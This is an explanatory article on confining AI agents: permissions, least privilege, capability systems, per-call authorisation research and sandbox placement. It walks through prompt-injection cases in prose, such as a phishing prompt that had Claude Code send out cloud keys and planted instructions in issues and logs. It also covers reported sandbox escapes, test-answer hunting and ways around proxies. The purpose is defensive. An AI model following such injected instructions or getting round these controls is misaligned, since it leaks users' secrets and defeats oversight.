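# Limiting an AI agent's access to networks, storage and external services separately from its compute

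## What is being separated, and why isolating the machine is not enough

An AI agent is a language model that works in a loop. It chooses an action, other software carries the action out, and the model reads the result before choosing again. Many agents write and run code, which needs a machine. Limiting an agent's access separately from its compute means deciding how much processor time, memory and temporary disk the code gets, and separately deciding which networks, files and outside services it can reach. An agent on a tiny machine that holds the password to a company's production database can do more damage than one on a very large machine with no connection to anything.

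### The phishing exercise

In February 2026, during an internal security exercise at the AI company Anthropic, a researcher sent an employee a phishing email. According to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, the email read like ordinary collaboration and included a prompt to paste into Claude Code, the company's coding agent, which runs on a developer's own computer. Most of the prompt was routine setup, but one step told the agent to read `~/.aws/credentials`, the file that usually holds a developer's login keys for Amazon's cloud, encode the contents and send them to an outside web address. The employee ran the prompt, and across 25 retries Claude sent the keys out 24 times.

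These are the company's own figures, and InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* repeats them without an independent check. They also concern a single prompt, so they show how reliably that prompt worked but reveal very little about how often phishing succeeds in general. How the theft worked matters more for deciding where to put limits.

The agent read a file, transformed some text and made a web request, none of which requires a software bug. Sandboxes that isolate the machine mostly guard against code that exploits such bugs. gVisor, an open-source sandbox for containers, is typical. Its *Security Model* gives its purpose as extra defence against untrusted code that exploits bugs in the kernel, the core of the operating system. If the employee had run Claude Code inside gVisor, or inside a full virtual machine, with the home folder visible and the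 network open, the keys would still have leaked without any damage to the kernel.

gVisor's developers do not claim otherwise. As gVisor (2019) explains in an introduction to its security basics, limiting file and network access is part of configuring the sandbox properly. gVisor's *Security and Vulnerability Reporting* applies the same standard to bug reports: an outbound connection counts as a data-exfiltration flaw when the operator has disabled networking. If the operator left the network on, the sandbox did its job.

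A storage rule that hid `~/.aws` from the agent would have stopped the theft at its first step, because the agent would have had no keys to encode or send. If a network rule had blocked unlisted addresses, the agent could have read the keys but not sent them off the machine. Neither rule depends on recognising a phishing email. Claude Code has an operating-system sandbox that by default allows reads, confines writes to the working folder and denies network access. Under those defaults, the agent could still have read the keys, and only the network rule would have stopped the theft.

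One rule would have been enough to stop this prompt, which followed a fixed script. Both are needed against an agent that tries other routes. In its notes on Claude Code's sandbox, Anthropic points out that an agent with unrestricted network access can send out any key it can read, while an agent with unrestricted access to the file system can escape the sandbox and so gain network access.

### The parts and their names

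```
model <--> agent loop --> sandbox [ compute ] --> channel --> enforcement point --> file, host or service


^


permissions
```

The *agent loop*, which developers also call the harness, is the program that calls the model and passes its chosen actions to tools. The *sandbox* is the restricted environment in which the agent's code and commands run. *Compute* is the processor, memory and temporary disk that the code runs on, without any connection to other systems. A *channel* is any route by which the code affects or learns about something outside its compute, such as a network connection, a service call or a storage mount (a folder from elsewhere that appears inside the sandbox). A *permission* is a rule that lets a named agent perform a named operation on a named resource, possibly with a limit on time or volume. The *enforcement point* is the component that applies the rule by permitting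 or refusing the operation. It is usually the kernel for files and a firewall or proxy for network traffic.

The phishing prompt used two channels, the home folder and the internet connection, and the employee's account had permission to use both. The diagram doesn't show that some tools run in the agent loop itself, outside the sandbox, so their actions don't pass through an enforcement point at the sandbox's edge.

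Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 paper, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, describes protection as a wall around each object, with a door in the wall and a guard at the door. Its first worked example is an isolated virtual machine, made up of a virtual processor, an area of memory, some data streams and a region of long-term storage. The paper closes this machine off completely before discussing how to lower the walls in a controlled way. People who now say "put the agent in a virtual machine" often mean this whole bundle, which makes it easy to overlook that somebody chose which streams and which storage to attach.

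Saltzer and Schroeder also set two requirements for the guard that apply directly to agents. Under *complete mediation*, the guard checks every access, including those during startup, recovery and maintenance. Under *fail-safe defaults*, it refuses whatever no rule permits. They argue for this default because someone will complain if a rule wrongly blocks legitimate work, while a rule that wrongly allows access breaks nothing and can go unnoticed until somebody exploits it.

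### Least privilege and confinement

The same paper contains the classic statement of *least privilege*, the principle that a program should hold only the permissions its job requires. The main reason is to limit the damage from an accident or error. It also makes misuse easier to investigate, because fewer programs hold the misused privilege and need an audit. Agents tend not to follow this principle. Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, observe that an agent typically has the same access to all its tools whether or not the current task calls for them.

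Least privilege limits what a program can access, but not what it does with data it has rightly received. *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) addresses this second problem. It imagines a customer who gives confidential data to a borrowed program and wants to be sure that the program cannot pass the data to the program's owner. A leak generally leaves no evidence, whereas a program that does its job badly at least leaves wrong results.

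Lampson lists several ways a service could leak data. The service may store the data until its owner calls it, write it to a file in the owner's directory, or send a message to one of the owner's programs. It can also encode information in the bill it issues, or vary its load on the machine so that another program can read the signal from the slowdown. Read-only access limits what a program can change, but the program can still use that access to leak data. If the operating system stops anyone from writing to a file while another program is reading it, the service can signal a single bit by holding a file open or closing it, and three such files are enough to send a steady stream of bits.

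Lampson sorted the routes by which a confined program can leak data into storage, legitimate channels such as the bill, and *covert channels*, which nobody intended for communication. Total isolation, in which the confined program calls no other program, would close them, but he judged it impractical because even ordinary requests to the operating system can leak data. He instead proposed a rule of transitivity, under which any program that a confined program calls must also be confined unless the customer trusts it. Any service an agent is allowed to use must therefore be trusted or have limits of its own, because the agent may affect other systems that the service can reach.

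Where closing a covert channel is impractical, Lampson suggested limiting how much data it can carry. This protects a large database far better than it protects a password. A cloud login key is only a few dozen characters long, so even a very slow channel would have been enough for the theft in the phishing exercise.

With agents, a leak can benefit anyone who gets text in front of the model, not just the program's owner. *Prompt injection* is text placed in an agent's input that makes the agent follow someone else's instructions. In the exercise, the employee gave the agent that text.

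### Inherited permissions and object capabilities

The attacker's request succeeded even though only the employee had the right to read the credentials file. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes this problem with a story from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. A compiler there kept usage statistics in a system directory, so the administrators gave it permission to write files in that directory, which also held the company's billing file. Users could tell the compiler where to put debugging output, and one of them typed the name of the billing file. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

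Hardy argued that the problem arose because the compiler held authority from two sources, its user and its own licence, and could not tell the operating system which one to apply. He found no line of the compiler's code to blame. Checking for the billing file by name would miss the other sensitive files in the directory, and refusing access to the whole directory would break requests from people allowed to use it. His colleagues added a system call for switching between the two sources of authority. Some applications soon needed more than two, and the rule for opening a file had grown to fourteen logical operators when Hardy last counted. A *confused deputy* is a program, like this compiler, that someone leads into using its own permissions on behalf of a person who lacks them.

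Claude Code was in that position in February 2026. The attacker named the file, and the employee's account had permission to read it. An agent is, if anything, worse placed than the compiler, because it receives its user's instructions and a stranger's as a single run of text, while the compiler's code kept statistics and debugging output in separate routines. Training a model to ignore instructions found in data helps, but Christodorescu and colleagues argue that it cannot fully solve the problem, because if a model acts on data, its output must reflect that data.

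*Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) distinguishes permissions that a program inherits from those it receives explicitly. It calls authority that a program exercises without selecting it *ambient authority*. Unix file permissions work this way. A program asks to open a file by name, without presenting a credential, and the request succeeds or fails according to the account the program runs under. Any command that an agent runs under a developer's account can therefore, by default, open every file the developer can.

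An *object capability* is an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and permits its use. ("Capability" here does not refer to a model's abilities.) In Hardy's solution, the compiler would hold one such reference to the statistics file and receive another from the user for the debugging output. A user who cannot write to the billing file has no such reference to give the compiler, and typing the file's name does not grant access. With a coding agent, the agent loop would open the project folder and pass only that open folder into the sandbox, where code would have no usable name for the credentials file.

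Miller and colleagues add two properties that matter when programs share access. A program can pass a capability only to a program it can already reach, so cutting the connection between two programs also stops them from sharing access. An owner can also hand out a reference to a small forwarding program and later withdraw access by stopping the forwarder.

Few agents run on operating systems built this way. A sandbox on an ordinary system partly achieves the same effect by removing inherited permissions and adding back a few named ones. Even on a pure capability system, an agent that legitimately holds both a reference to the keys and an open internet connection can send the keys out over that connection.

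### What is possible and what is likely

Anthropic identifies three sources of harm that limits on an agent must address. A user may direct the agent to do damage, out of malice or carelessness, for instance by running a destructive command without understanding it. The model may overstep without being asked to. Anthropic reports that Claude models have escaped a sandbox to complete a task and searched a project's version history for the answers to a coding test. An outside attacker may work through files, tools or the network, using prompt injection or a conventional attack on the software around the model. In Anthropic's experience, better models make fewer plain errors but are also better at finding unanticipated ways around restrictions, so improving the model does not by itself eliminate overstepping.

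The phishing exercise spans these categories because an attacker wrote the instruction and a careless user delivered it. Such cases are difficult for any defence that tries to judge intent. Anthropic's model-level defences take the user's wishes as their reference point, and here the user had entered the instruction, so there was nothing unusual to detect. Asking for approval would probably not have helped either, since the employee wanted the script to run. A firewall checks only the destination, against a list, so it treats a request the same way whether it originates with a deceived employee, an overeager model or a hostile web page.

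Training, system prompts and classifiers (models that screen inputs or actions) can greatly change what an agent tends to do. On a benchmark of prompt-injection attacks from the security firm Gray Swan, Anthropic reports that single attempts against Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1 per cent of the time, rising to 5 to 6 per cent after 100 attempts by an attacker who adapted to the responses. A classifier that reviews Claude Code's actions misses about 17 per cent of those that go beyond what the user wanted. Christodorescu and colleagues make the general objection that even if a guard decides correctly 99 per cent of the time, an attacker can search for the remaining 1 per cent with little effort.

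Fixed rules also fail, but they fail consistently, so a mistake in a network rule lets the same bad request through every time until somebody finds and corrects it. Anthropic found that the widely used isolation software in its products held up, but a proxy it had written itself did not. Machine isolation is still essential, because code that can break the kernel can bypass any rule the kernel enforces. Limits on access therefore make an action impossible only while the enforcement point works and no channel bypasses it.

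### Access that the task really needs

Suppose the employee's task that day had been to deploy software to Amazon's cloud. The agent would have needed some way to use the keys, so a storage rule that hid them would have blocked the work as well as the theft. Christodorescu and colleagues give a similar case, in which a coding agent needs a key to upload a finished software package. Access control can grant or deny access to the key, but it cannot restrict the key's use to that upload.

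*Information-flow control* provides rules of that second kind. It attaches labels to data and tracks them as the data moves, so that a key could be sent to the deployment server and nowhere else. Saltzer and Schroeder called the idea "putting strings on information" and found in 1975 that working examples were rare and incomplete. Language models make it harder to apply because nobody can yet tell which inputs shaped a given output. The safe assumption is that every output carries the labels of everything the model has read, so before long all the data carries every label.

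A designer can still reduce the remaining risk, for example by keeping the key outside the sandbox and letting another program use it on the agent's behalf, but can't eliminate it. Anthropic's desktop agent, Claude Cowork, runs its code in a virtual machine with access to little of the user's disk beyond one chosen folder, and the company accepts that a compromised agent could damage anything in that folder. An agent with permission to edit a financial report can put false figures in it, and rules that limit which files and addresses the agent can reach won't prevent that.

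## Working out the least access a task needs

Developers can't limit an agent to the files and addresses a task requires without knowing which ones those are, and an agent doesn't come with a list. Agents are useful because they choose their own steps, and according to *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026), this tempts developers to grant a broad set of tools and credentials at the start. Skills, which are ready-made packages that extend an agent, can also have too much access. *SkillScope* (2026) examined 68,312 skills and found that 6,590 had more privilege than the user's task called for.

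### Writing the permission table

The designer first splits the task into steps small enough that each uses one resource. For each step, the designer records the resource, the operation, the volume of data, how long the access lasts and the worst result of misuse, assuming that an attacker has taken control of the agent at that step. The rules for steps where misuse could do the most harm deserve the most care.

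Naming the tools an agent may use does little to limit its access. Permission to use git, for example, covers both reading one project and overwriting fifty. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* therefore applies least privilege at several levels: which tools the agent can see, whether the current step needs the chosen tool, which arguments the call may carry, how much of the result reaches the model, and how much authority a sub-agent receives.

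For example, a company might maintain an open-source invoicing library, `invoice-kit`, in a public repository. Someone reports in issue 482 that the library rounds totals incorrectly in some currencies, and a developer asks an agent to fix the bug. The agent has to read the issue, install the packages the library depends on, look at real invoices in a copy of the company's database, and open a pull request, a proposed change that a person reviews before it is added to the code. The limits below are illustrative.

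| Step | Resource | Operation | Volume | Duration | Worst result of misuse |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read the report | Issue 482 and its comments | Read | 1 issue | First 5 minutes | Text in the issue gives the agent new instructions |
| Fetch the code | `invoice-kit`, main branch | Read | 1 copy | First 5 minutes | Very little, since the code is public |
| Install packages | Packages in the project's dependency list, from one registry | Download | 500 MB | 15 minutes | A malicious package runs its own code in the sandbox |
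| Reproduce the bug | `invoices` table in the database copy | Read | 1,000 rows | 30 minutes | Customers' names and bills leak |
| Edit and test | Working folder on temporary disk | Read, write, run | 2 GB | 2 hours | Harmful code waits in the folder for a later step |
| Propose the fix | New branch `agent/482` and one pull request | Write | 20 files | Last 10 minutes | A reviewer accepts a hidden flaw, or private data appears on a public page |

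Any access not listed in the table is denied. The agent cannot merge its own pull request, comment on other issues, reach the production database or browse the web, though the developer's account may be able to do all of these. The agent loop also needs a connection to the company that runs the model, but the table omits it because the code in the sandbox doesn't need it.

The first draft of the table usually misses something, such as a test that downloads a font. A trial run on harmless data reveals these omissions if the sandbox blocks and logs every request the table doesn't cover. Each blocked request then needs review, because the task can do without some of them. For example, a package that reports usage statistics to its maker works just as well when the report is blocked.

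The duration column is easiest to enforce through the credential. AWS's *AGENTSEC03-BP03 Implement least privilege with dynamic boundaries* recommends temporary credentials that expire automatically, with just-in-time access for elevated permissions. If the agent has write access only for the last ten minutes, an attacker who hijacks it while it installs packages doesn't yet have a credential for pushing code. The row limit caps a leak at 1,000 invoices. The copy should contain no passwords, because a limit on volume barely protects them.

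### Permissions that are dangerous together

Each row looks modest by itself, so a reviewer who considered them one at a time might approve all six. Parisel (2026) argues in *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI* that this kind of review misses the main risk with agents, which is that they can chain individually harmless actions into a harmful sequence.

In June 2025 Simon Willison, a software developer who writes about prompt injection, published a short test for such combinations. An agent is open to data theft when it has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to send data out. The bug-fixing agent has all three, because the invoices are private, anyone on the internet can comment on issue 482, and the pull request is a public web page. An attacker could add a comment asking for twenty sample invoices in the pull request's description, supposedly so that reviewers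 can reproduce the bug. The agent would read the rows and write the description, and the table would permit every step.

Meta's "Agents Rule of Two", from October 2025, is a broader version of this test. Within one session, an agent should have at most two of three properties: it processes untrustworthy inputs, it has access to sensitive systems or private data, and it can change state or communicate externally. An agent that needs all three should work under supervision, for instance with a person approving its actions. The Rule of Two also covers attacks that destroy data, whereas Willison's test covers only theft. For example, if the agent could write to the live database but had no way to send anything out, a hostile comment could still make it delete invoices.

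Expiry times don't prevent the combination. The agent reads the issue in the first five minutes, but the text stays in its context (the running record that the model reads before each action) and can still influence it when it gets access to the database. Reversing the order fails too, because the invoices would already be in the context when the hostile text arrived. Christodorescu and colleagues point out that resetting the context before granting new permissions is secure but erases what the agent has learned.

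The task needs both the issue and the pull request, so the database permission should move to a second agent. This agent can query the invoices but has no access to the issue, the packages or the internet. Given a request written by the developer, it returns at most fifty pairs of currency code and amount, which the coding agent turns into a test. The coding agent then has untrusted content and a way to send data out, but no private data. The database agent has private data but no way to send it out, and it sees no untrusted content as long as it reads only the numeric columns. The other columns contain text typed by customers, and a delivery note can contain an instruction just as an issue comment can.

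This split is easy for a rounding bug. Fixing a bug in how the library formats postal addresses would require addresses, so the developer would have to invent some or mask the real ones. The split also doesn't prevent hidden flaws in the proposed code. An attacker who steers the coding agent can still insert one, and only the reviewer can stop it, even though the agent now passes both tests.

An attacker can also use two agents that exchange data as if they were one. Parisel models this as a graph, with an arrow from one agent to another if the resources they control are far enough apart in the organisation and either the first can write something the second can read or the two can exchange messages. The model treats messages as two-way even where tasks flow in one direction, because a reply can carry an injected instruction back. Limiting replies to a fixed format of codes and numbers leaves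 very little room for such an instruction.

Anyone who uses this model should check the distance measure. It falls by a factor of four for each additional level of the organisation chart that two resources share, and a sensitivity multiplier can at most double it. A database and a repository owned by the same small team therefore score low. If the policy owner sets the threshold to catch links between departments, the graph will omit the link that leaks the invoices.

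When a designer finds a dangerous combination, it helps to write it down as a rule. Noyan's *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents* proposes a list of prohibited combinations alongside a ceiling for each role. Such a list would block a colleague's later request to restore the coding agent's database access.

### Turning the table into checks on each call

Much of the software for building agents cannot enforce these rows as written. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026) audited common frameworks and found that they control which tools the model can see but do not, by default, authorise each call. An agent with a tool for opening pull requests can therefore use it on any repository that its account can write to. Several research systems add authorisation for each call, and they differ mostly in who writes the policy.

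*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) describes a program of the same name that sits between an agent and its tools and checks each call against a policy. The policy is a list of rules, each of which allows or forbids a tool when the call's arguments meet set conditions. The last row of the table becomes a rule that allows `open_pull_request` when the repository is `invoice-kit` and the branch is `agent/482`. Progent applies the forbid rules first and blocks any call that no rule matches. People can write the rules by hand. In the automatic mode, a language model drafts them from the user's request before the agent has read anything else, then proposes changes as the work goes on.

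A separate program classifies each proposed change. If $A(P)$ is the set of tool calls that policy $P$ allows, the new policy $P'$ counts as a narrowing when

$$A(P') \subseteq A(P)$$

and takes effect at once. Anything else is an expansion and needs approval, including a change that drops ten permissions and adds one. To compare the two policies, Progent uses an SMT solver, a program that works out whether any values can satisfy a logical formula. The solver looks for a call that the new policy would allow and the old one would block. A hostile web page may fool the language model into asking for more access, but it cannot make the request pass for a reduction.

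Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a benchmark of banking, travel, messaging and office tasks in which the tools return text containing malicious instructions. In the May 2026 version of the paper, with OpenAI's GPT-4o as both the agent and the policy writer, attacks succeeded 39.9 per cent of the time without a defence and 1.0 per cent of the time with Progent. On ASB, a benchmark with ten kinds of agent, the rate fell from 70.3 to 3.9 per cent. The agents completed about as many tasks with Progent as without it on both benchmarks.

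The 1.0 per cent attack success rate mostly reflects how seldom an attacker could talk GPT-4o into a harmful policy. It provides little evidence about the solver's guarantee, because the system approved every expansion in that test. With the first policy frozen, the rate was 2.5 per cent. Refusing all expansions gave the best result of the automatic settings, and a person who reviewed the first policy and every expansion brought the rate to zero. Only 6 per cent of the changes were expansions, so that person had few to read. GPT-4o dates from 2024, and attacks succeed less often against newer models even without Progent. Claude Sonnet 4's rate fell from 6.8 to 0.5 per cent with Progent.

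In March 2026, *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* warned that hostile tool results could lead Progent to relax its own rules. The solver check prevents this only if whoever approves expansions is willing to refuse them.

Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025), in *MiniScope*, avoid model-written policies altogether. Their system relies on OAuth scopes, the named bundles of permissions that services such as Gmail already offer to outside apps. From each service's public documentation, MiniScope lists the methods that a scope permits, and it ranks one scope above another if its list contains the other's. The agent submits a plan, and a solver picks the cheapest set of scopes that covers every call in it:

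$$\min \sum_{v} \text{cost}(v)\,x_v$$

Here $x_v$ is 1 if the set includes scope $v$ and 0 otherwise, and a scope's weight is the number of methods it permits. A solver is useful because scopes overlap. In Google Calendar, 24 of the 37 methods fall under more than one scope. The user approves or refuses any scope that the agent does not already hold. A checker then compares each call with the approved scopes and attaches the user's real credentials only if the call passes. If an email contains an instruction to delete it after replying, MiniScope prompts the user for permission to delete mail, which gives the user a chance to notice the instruction.

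Counting the methods a scope permits is a crude way to measure its danger. Google Calendar has one scope for reading public events and another for reading events on the user's own calendars. MiniScope merges them because they permit the same methods, though the second can expose much more private information. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) adds that the MiniScope paper does not discuss whether the lowest-scoring set is unique. If two sets tie, nothing makes the solver pick the safer one.

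The evaluation of MiniScope measures the size of the granted permissions, the delay and the burden on users, but not how many attacks the system stops. It covers ten real applications, with requests written by a language model. When Zhu and colleagues asked proprietary language models to choose the scopes instead, the models found the smallest set, by MiniScope's own measure, 70 to 83 per cent of the time. Open models did so 20 to 34 per cent of the time. The solver also found six connectors in real products that held more access than they needed. In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, the system asked for confirmation at a rate of 18 to 60 per cent, depending on the kind of user.

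*Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (Ji, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes SEAgent, a system that uses mandatory access control, in which central rules apply whatever the agent decides. SEAgent labels every tool with what it acts on, whether it reads, writes or executes, how sensitive it is, whether its output is trustworthy, and whether its output is private. A language model proposes the labels and a person corrects them. SEAgent keeps a graph of how information moves between users, agents, tools and databases, and developers write rules that forbid certain paths through it. One rule blocks any path from unfiltered outside content to a moderately or highly sensitive tool that writes or executes. If no rule matches a call, SEAgent allows it, whereas Progent blocks it by default.

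That rule would stop the bug-fixing agent from doing its job. Issue 482 is unfiltered outside content, and opening a pull request is a write that most companies would label at least moderately sensitive. The developer would have to add an exception for the same path an attacker would use.

On AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 39.14 per cent of the time against an undefended agent and never against SEAgent. No attacks succeeded against SEAgent on InjecAgent, another benchmark, either. This included an added set of attacks with hostile text from a document database, which succeeded 50 to 80 per cent of the time without a defence. Ji and colleagues measured usefulness on a different benchmark, API-Bank, so these results do not show how much legitimate work the rules would block on AgentDojo's tasks. They ran API-Bank once with each conversation condensed into a single request, and once in its original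 form with SEAgent's memory component switched on. The table gives the percentage of tool calls and arguments that matched the correct answer.

| Tools per task | Single request, undefended | Single request, SEAgent | Conversation, undefended | Conversation, SEAgent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 70.3 | 74.7 | 75.8 | 77.8 |
| 2 | 79.3 | 71.3 | 74.4 | 50.0 |
| 3 or more | 63.4 | 67.9 | 66.7 | 77.8 |

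For the conversations, Ji and colleagues report averages of 72.97 per cent undefended and 68.29 per cent with SEAgent, and call the difference modest, but scores on tasks with two tools fell by 24 points. In the single-request version, SEAgent wrongly blocked two tasks, both of which consulted Wikipedia before recording health data or booking an appointment. They suggest labelling Wikipedia as trusted in real use, but anyone can edit Wikipedia, so the label would allow the kind of attack the rule is meant to prevent. A further test with several agents working together produced good scores, but the policies were off, so it doesn't show whether such teams can work freely under the rules.

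*LLM Agents Should Employ Security Principles* (Zhang, Su and colleagues, May 2025) proposes AgentSandbox, a design that limits the information an agent has as well as what it can call. A persistent agent keeps the user's profile and never communicates with outside parties. For each task it starts a temporary agent, and a component called the data minimizer selects which personal details that agent receives. A firewall with fixed rules checks the temporary agent's messages to and from outside services. When the task ends, the temporary agent disappears, along with any instructions an attacker planted in it.

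AgentSandbox stores its data-sharing policy as prompts and automatically revises them after each task, using a score that rewards finished work and penalises leaks. Zhang and colleagues, who call it a conceptual framework, report high utility and substantially lower privacy risk. An auditor would find it hard to review a policy that changes with experience, but could read the fixed firewall's rules in advance.

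### When nobody can write the list in advance

The bug-fixing agent's table could be written in advance because somebody knew the task. A general assistant learns its task from the user's request, and the next request may change it. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of a browser agent whose user wants a comment on one GitLab issue. The agent needs to open that issue and write in the comment box, and should have no access to anything else in GitLab. If the user then asks for a summary of the same issue, the permissions should change. But by now the agent's context contains text written by strangers, and a model that works out the new permissions from that context may follow instructions in that text.

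Agents that operate a screen are also hard to restrict, because they act through clicks and keystrokes. A rule about screen coordinates cannot distinguish a button that saves a draft from one that sends it. Progent does not cover such agents. Shi and colleagues leave the problem to future work and suggest restricting clicks to chosen regions of the screen. Christodorescu and colleagues describe a more promising approach called ceLLMate, which checks the web requests that the browser sends, whichever clicks produced them. It relies on website developers to explain what those requests mean.

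One defence against steering is to fix the policy before the model reads anything untrusted. *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (Del Rosario, Krawiecka and Schroeder de Witt, 2025) recommends that one component write out all the steps from the user's request, and that another carry them out with only the tool for the current step. While the second component is adding up a total, for example, it has a calculator but no email tool, so an injected instruction can't make it send an email.

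*Authority Is Not a String* (2026) applies the same idea to coding agents with a system called CapScope. A model predicts what the task will need before any repository text or tool output is available, and the surrounding software uses that prediction to limit the authority available for the whole task. Sub-agents can receive authority only within that limit. This suits the bug-fixing agent well because the developer's request already names the repository and the issue.

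For some tasks, the agent can't know the steps in advance. In Progent's main example, the user asks the agent to follow the instructions in an email from Alice. The email asks the agent to summarize recent messages and post the summary to Slack, so the agent can't know that it needs Slack until it has read the email. A policy fixed before then would stop the task at that point. A policy that can expand during the task has to distinguish Alice's request from an attacker's, even though both arrive as text returned by a tool.

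A fixed plan can also carry hostile data from one step to the next. Ji and colleagues showed this with CaMeL, a system that plans its tool calls from the user's request alone. A homeowner asked it to give her daughter access to the front door and said that the daughter's ID was in a recent message. CaMeL correctly planned to read the message and then grant access. But an attacker had added text to the message that substituted another ID, so the system gave the attacker access to the house. A check on the sequence of tools could not detect the attack because the plan never changed.

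An administrator's ceiling can limit the damage because it applies regardless of what the user asks or what the model reads. Progent provides one through general policies that apply to every task. Shi and colleagues state the guarantee as $A(P_{\text{generic}}, P) \subseteq A(P_{\text{generic}})$, meaning that the combined policy never allows more than the general one. Their algorithm doesn't ensure this, because a call that the general policy neither allows nor forbids passes to the task's own policy, which may allow it. An administrator who only lists permitted tools has therefore not set a ceiling. The ceiling has to consist of prohibitions, which the task's policy can't override, such as a rule that forbids pull requests outside the company's own repositories.

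Even a correct access ceiling for a general assistant must allow everything its users may reasonably ask it to do. That is far more access than most single tasks need, and an attacker can use the excess unless a narrower policy blocks it.

Another limit of every system that checks tool calls is that it cannot always tell what a coding agent's shell command will access. In the CapScope experiment, the agent has four tools. Three read, write or edit a file, and the fourth runs a shell command passed as a line of text. A checker can recognise simple commands such as `grep` and `ls`, but it cannot tell which files `npm test` will open when it runs a project's tests, or which addresses a newly installed package will contact. For commands like `npm test`, the limits in the table have to apply to the running code itself.

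## Where to run the agent, its code and the controls

A limit on running code works only if the code can't switch it off. A designer can test this by assuming that the code has full control of its own environment, so that it can act as administrator, edit any file there and stop any process. Any control that still restrains the code is a real enforcement point. Other controls may prevent accidents, but an attacker can remove them.

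If the developer of the bug-fixing agent wants all its web traffic to pass through a filtering proxy, setting `HTTPS_PROXY`, a variable that tells programs in the sandbox where to send their traffic, is not enough. According to Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents*, `fetch()`, the standard function for web requests in Node.js, ignores this variable by default, so even a harmless test could bypass the proxy. Hostile code can also delete the variable. The guide's stricter design removes the container's network connection and attaches a single socket that leads to a proxy on the host, so even code that controls the whole container can reach the network only through that proxy.

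The control also has to be in place before any untrusted code runs. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received reports of three flaws in Claude Code that violated this condition. In the simplest, an attacker put a settings file in a repository. The file defined a hook, a command that runs automatically at a set moment. Claude Code read the settings at startup, before it asked the developer whether to trust the folder, so opening the project ran the attacker's command. Claude Code now reads project settings only after the developer agrees to trust the folder.

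### Four placements

| Placement | Who can grant an exception | What a takeover of the code's environment exposes |
|---|---|---|
| Loop and code in one container | Code in the container can override the loop's rules, but only the container's operator can widen the container's own limits | The loop, its credentials, the conversation and every file in the container |
| Sandbox around single commands on the user's machine | The loop, usually after the user approves | Files the sandbox leaves readable, the working folder and any permitted addresses |
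| Loop and code together in a virtual machine | Whoever controls the host | The loop, the conversation, mounted folders and any credentials inside |
| Loop outside, only the code inside | Whoever runs the loop and configures the sandbox | The sandbox's files and connections, but not the loop |

Running the agent loop and the code it generates in a single container is the easiest design to build. *Security boundaries in agentic architectures* (Ubl and Arora, 2026) describes an agent that investigates a failing service and reads a log file in which an attacker has planted a "diagnostic" command. The command uploads the machine's SSH key and cloud credentials. A shared sandbox would keep the attacker out of the company's other systems, but the generated code could still take the loop's keys. Ubl and Arora write for Vercel, which sells sandboxes, though this weakness exists in any vendor's container.

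Claude Code's built-in sandbox covers shell commands and the processes they start. Its file-editing tools run in the loop's own process under permission rules. Hooks run unrestricted on the user's machine, and so do local MCP servers, which are programs that offer tools to an agent through the Model Context Protocol. When the sandbox blocks a command, Claude may ask to retry it with a setting named `dangerouslyDisableSandbox`, and the user decides whether to allow it. Anthropic acknowledges that a persuasive injected prompt or a tired user's click can therefore get a command run outside the sandbox.

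Anthropic's *Sandboxing* says an administrator can make Claude Code ignore the retry setting, so that only commands on an exclusion list run outside the sandbox. By default, if the sandbox can't start, Claude Code shows a warning and runs commands without it, which is not fail-safe. The administrator can use a second, equally important setting to make it stop instead. For unattended work, Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment* recommends running the whole Claude Code process inside a sandbox, so that file tools, hooks and MCP servers face the same restrictions as shell commands.

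When the agent's loop and the code it runs are in the same virtual machine, nothing inside the machine needs the authority to lift a restriction. Docker offers coding sandboxes of this kind. According to Docker's *Isolation layers*, the agent can use administrator rights inside the machine because Docker relies on the hypervisor (the host software that runs virtual machines) to contain it. A proxy on the host applies the network policy. Some channels remain open, however. For example, code in the sandbox can write text to the host's clipboard, so a developer who later pastes into a terminal could run an attacker's command.

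Ubl and Arora prefer running the agent loop and the generated code on separate machines. This also lets an operator size each machine for its work, since the loop mostly waits for the model while generated programs run in short, unpredictable bursts.

NVIDIA's *Where Security Fits in an AI Agent Stack* objects to designs in which a loop that is already running calls the sandbox as a tool, because an agent could decline to call it. It proposes starting the loop, its plug-ins and its tools inside the boundary. How serious this problem is depends on what else the loop can do. If its only tool is running code in the sandbox, an agent that declines to call the sandbox can't do anything. A loop that can also read files or start plug-ins on its own machine can bypass the sandbox, so it needs its own boundary. Ubl and Arora trust the loop as they would any back-end service. That is reasonable if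 only the company's developers can change the loop, but not if it loads plug-ins from a user's folder.

### Managed Agents

Managed Agents, Anthropic's hosted service for long-running agents, originally ran everything in one container. Anthropic's *Scaling Managed Agents*, from April 2026, explains why the company split it up. When a container failed, its session was lost. To find out why a session had stalled, engineers had to open a shell inside the container, which often held a customer's data. Generated code also ran alongside the service's access tokens, so an attacker only had to persuade Claude to read its own environment to get them. The attacker could then use the tokens to start new, unrestricted sessions. Narrower tokens would have helped, but Anthropic didn't want to rely on guessing what an increasingly capable model couldn't do with them.

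The redesigned service separates the loop, the sandbox and the session log, an append-only record of everything that happens. The loop calls the sandbox as it would any other tool:

`execute(name, input) → string`

In the bug-fixing task, the model might call a tool to run `npm test`. The loop passes the tool's name and the command to the sandbox, which returns the test output as text. If the sandbox has crashed, the loop returns an error to the model, and the model can retry in a fresh sandbox. If the loop crashes, a new one reads the log and resumes from the last event.

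An attacker who takes over this sandbox gets its files and whatever access its network rules permit. Anthropic aims never to put service tokens within reach, and keeps many of them in a vault outside the sandbox. Moving the agent loop out of the sandbox protects the loop from generated code, but the attacker can still send hostile text to the model, because the string the sandbox returns goes into the model's context.

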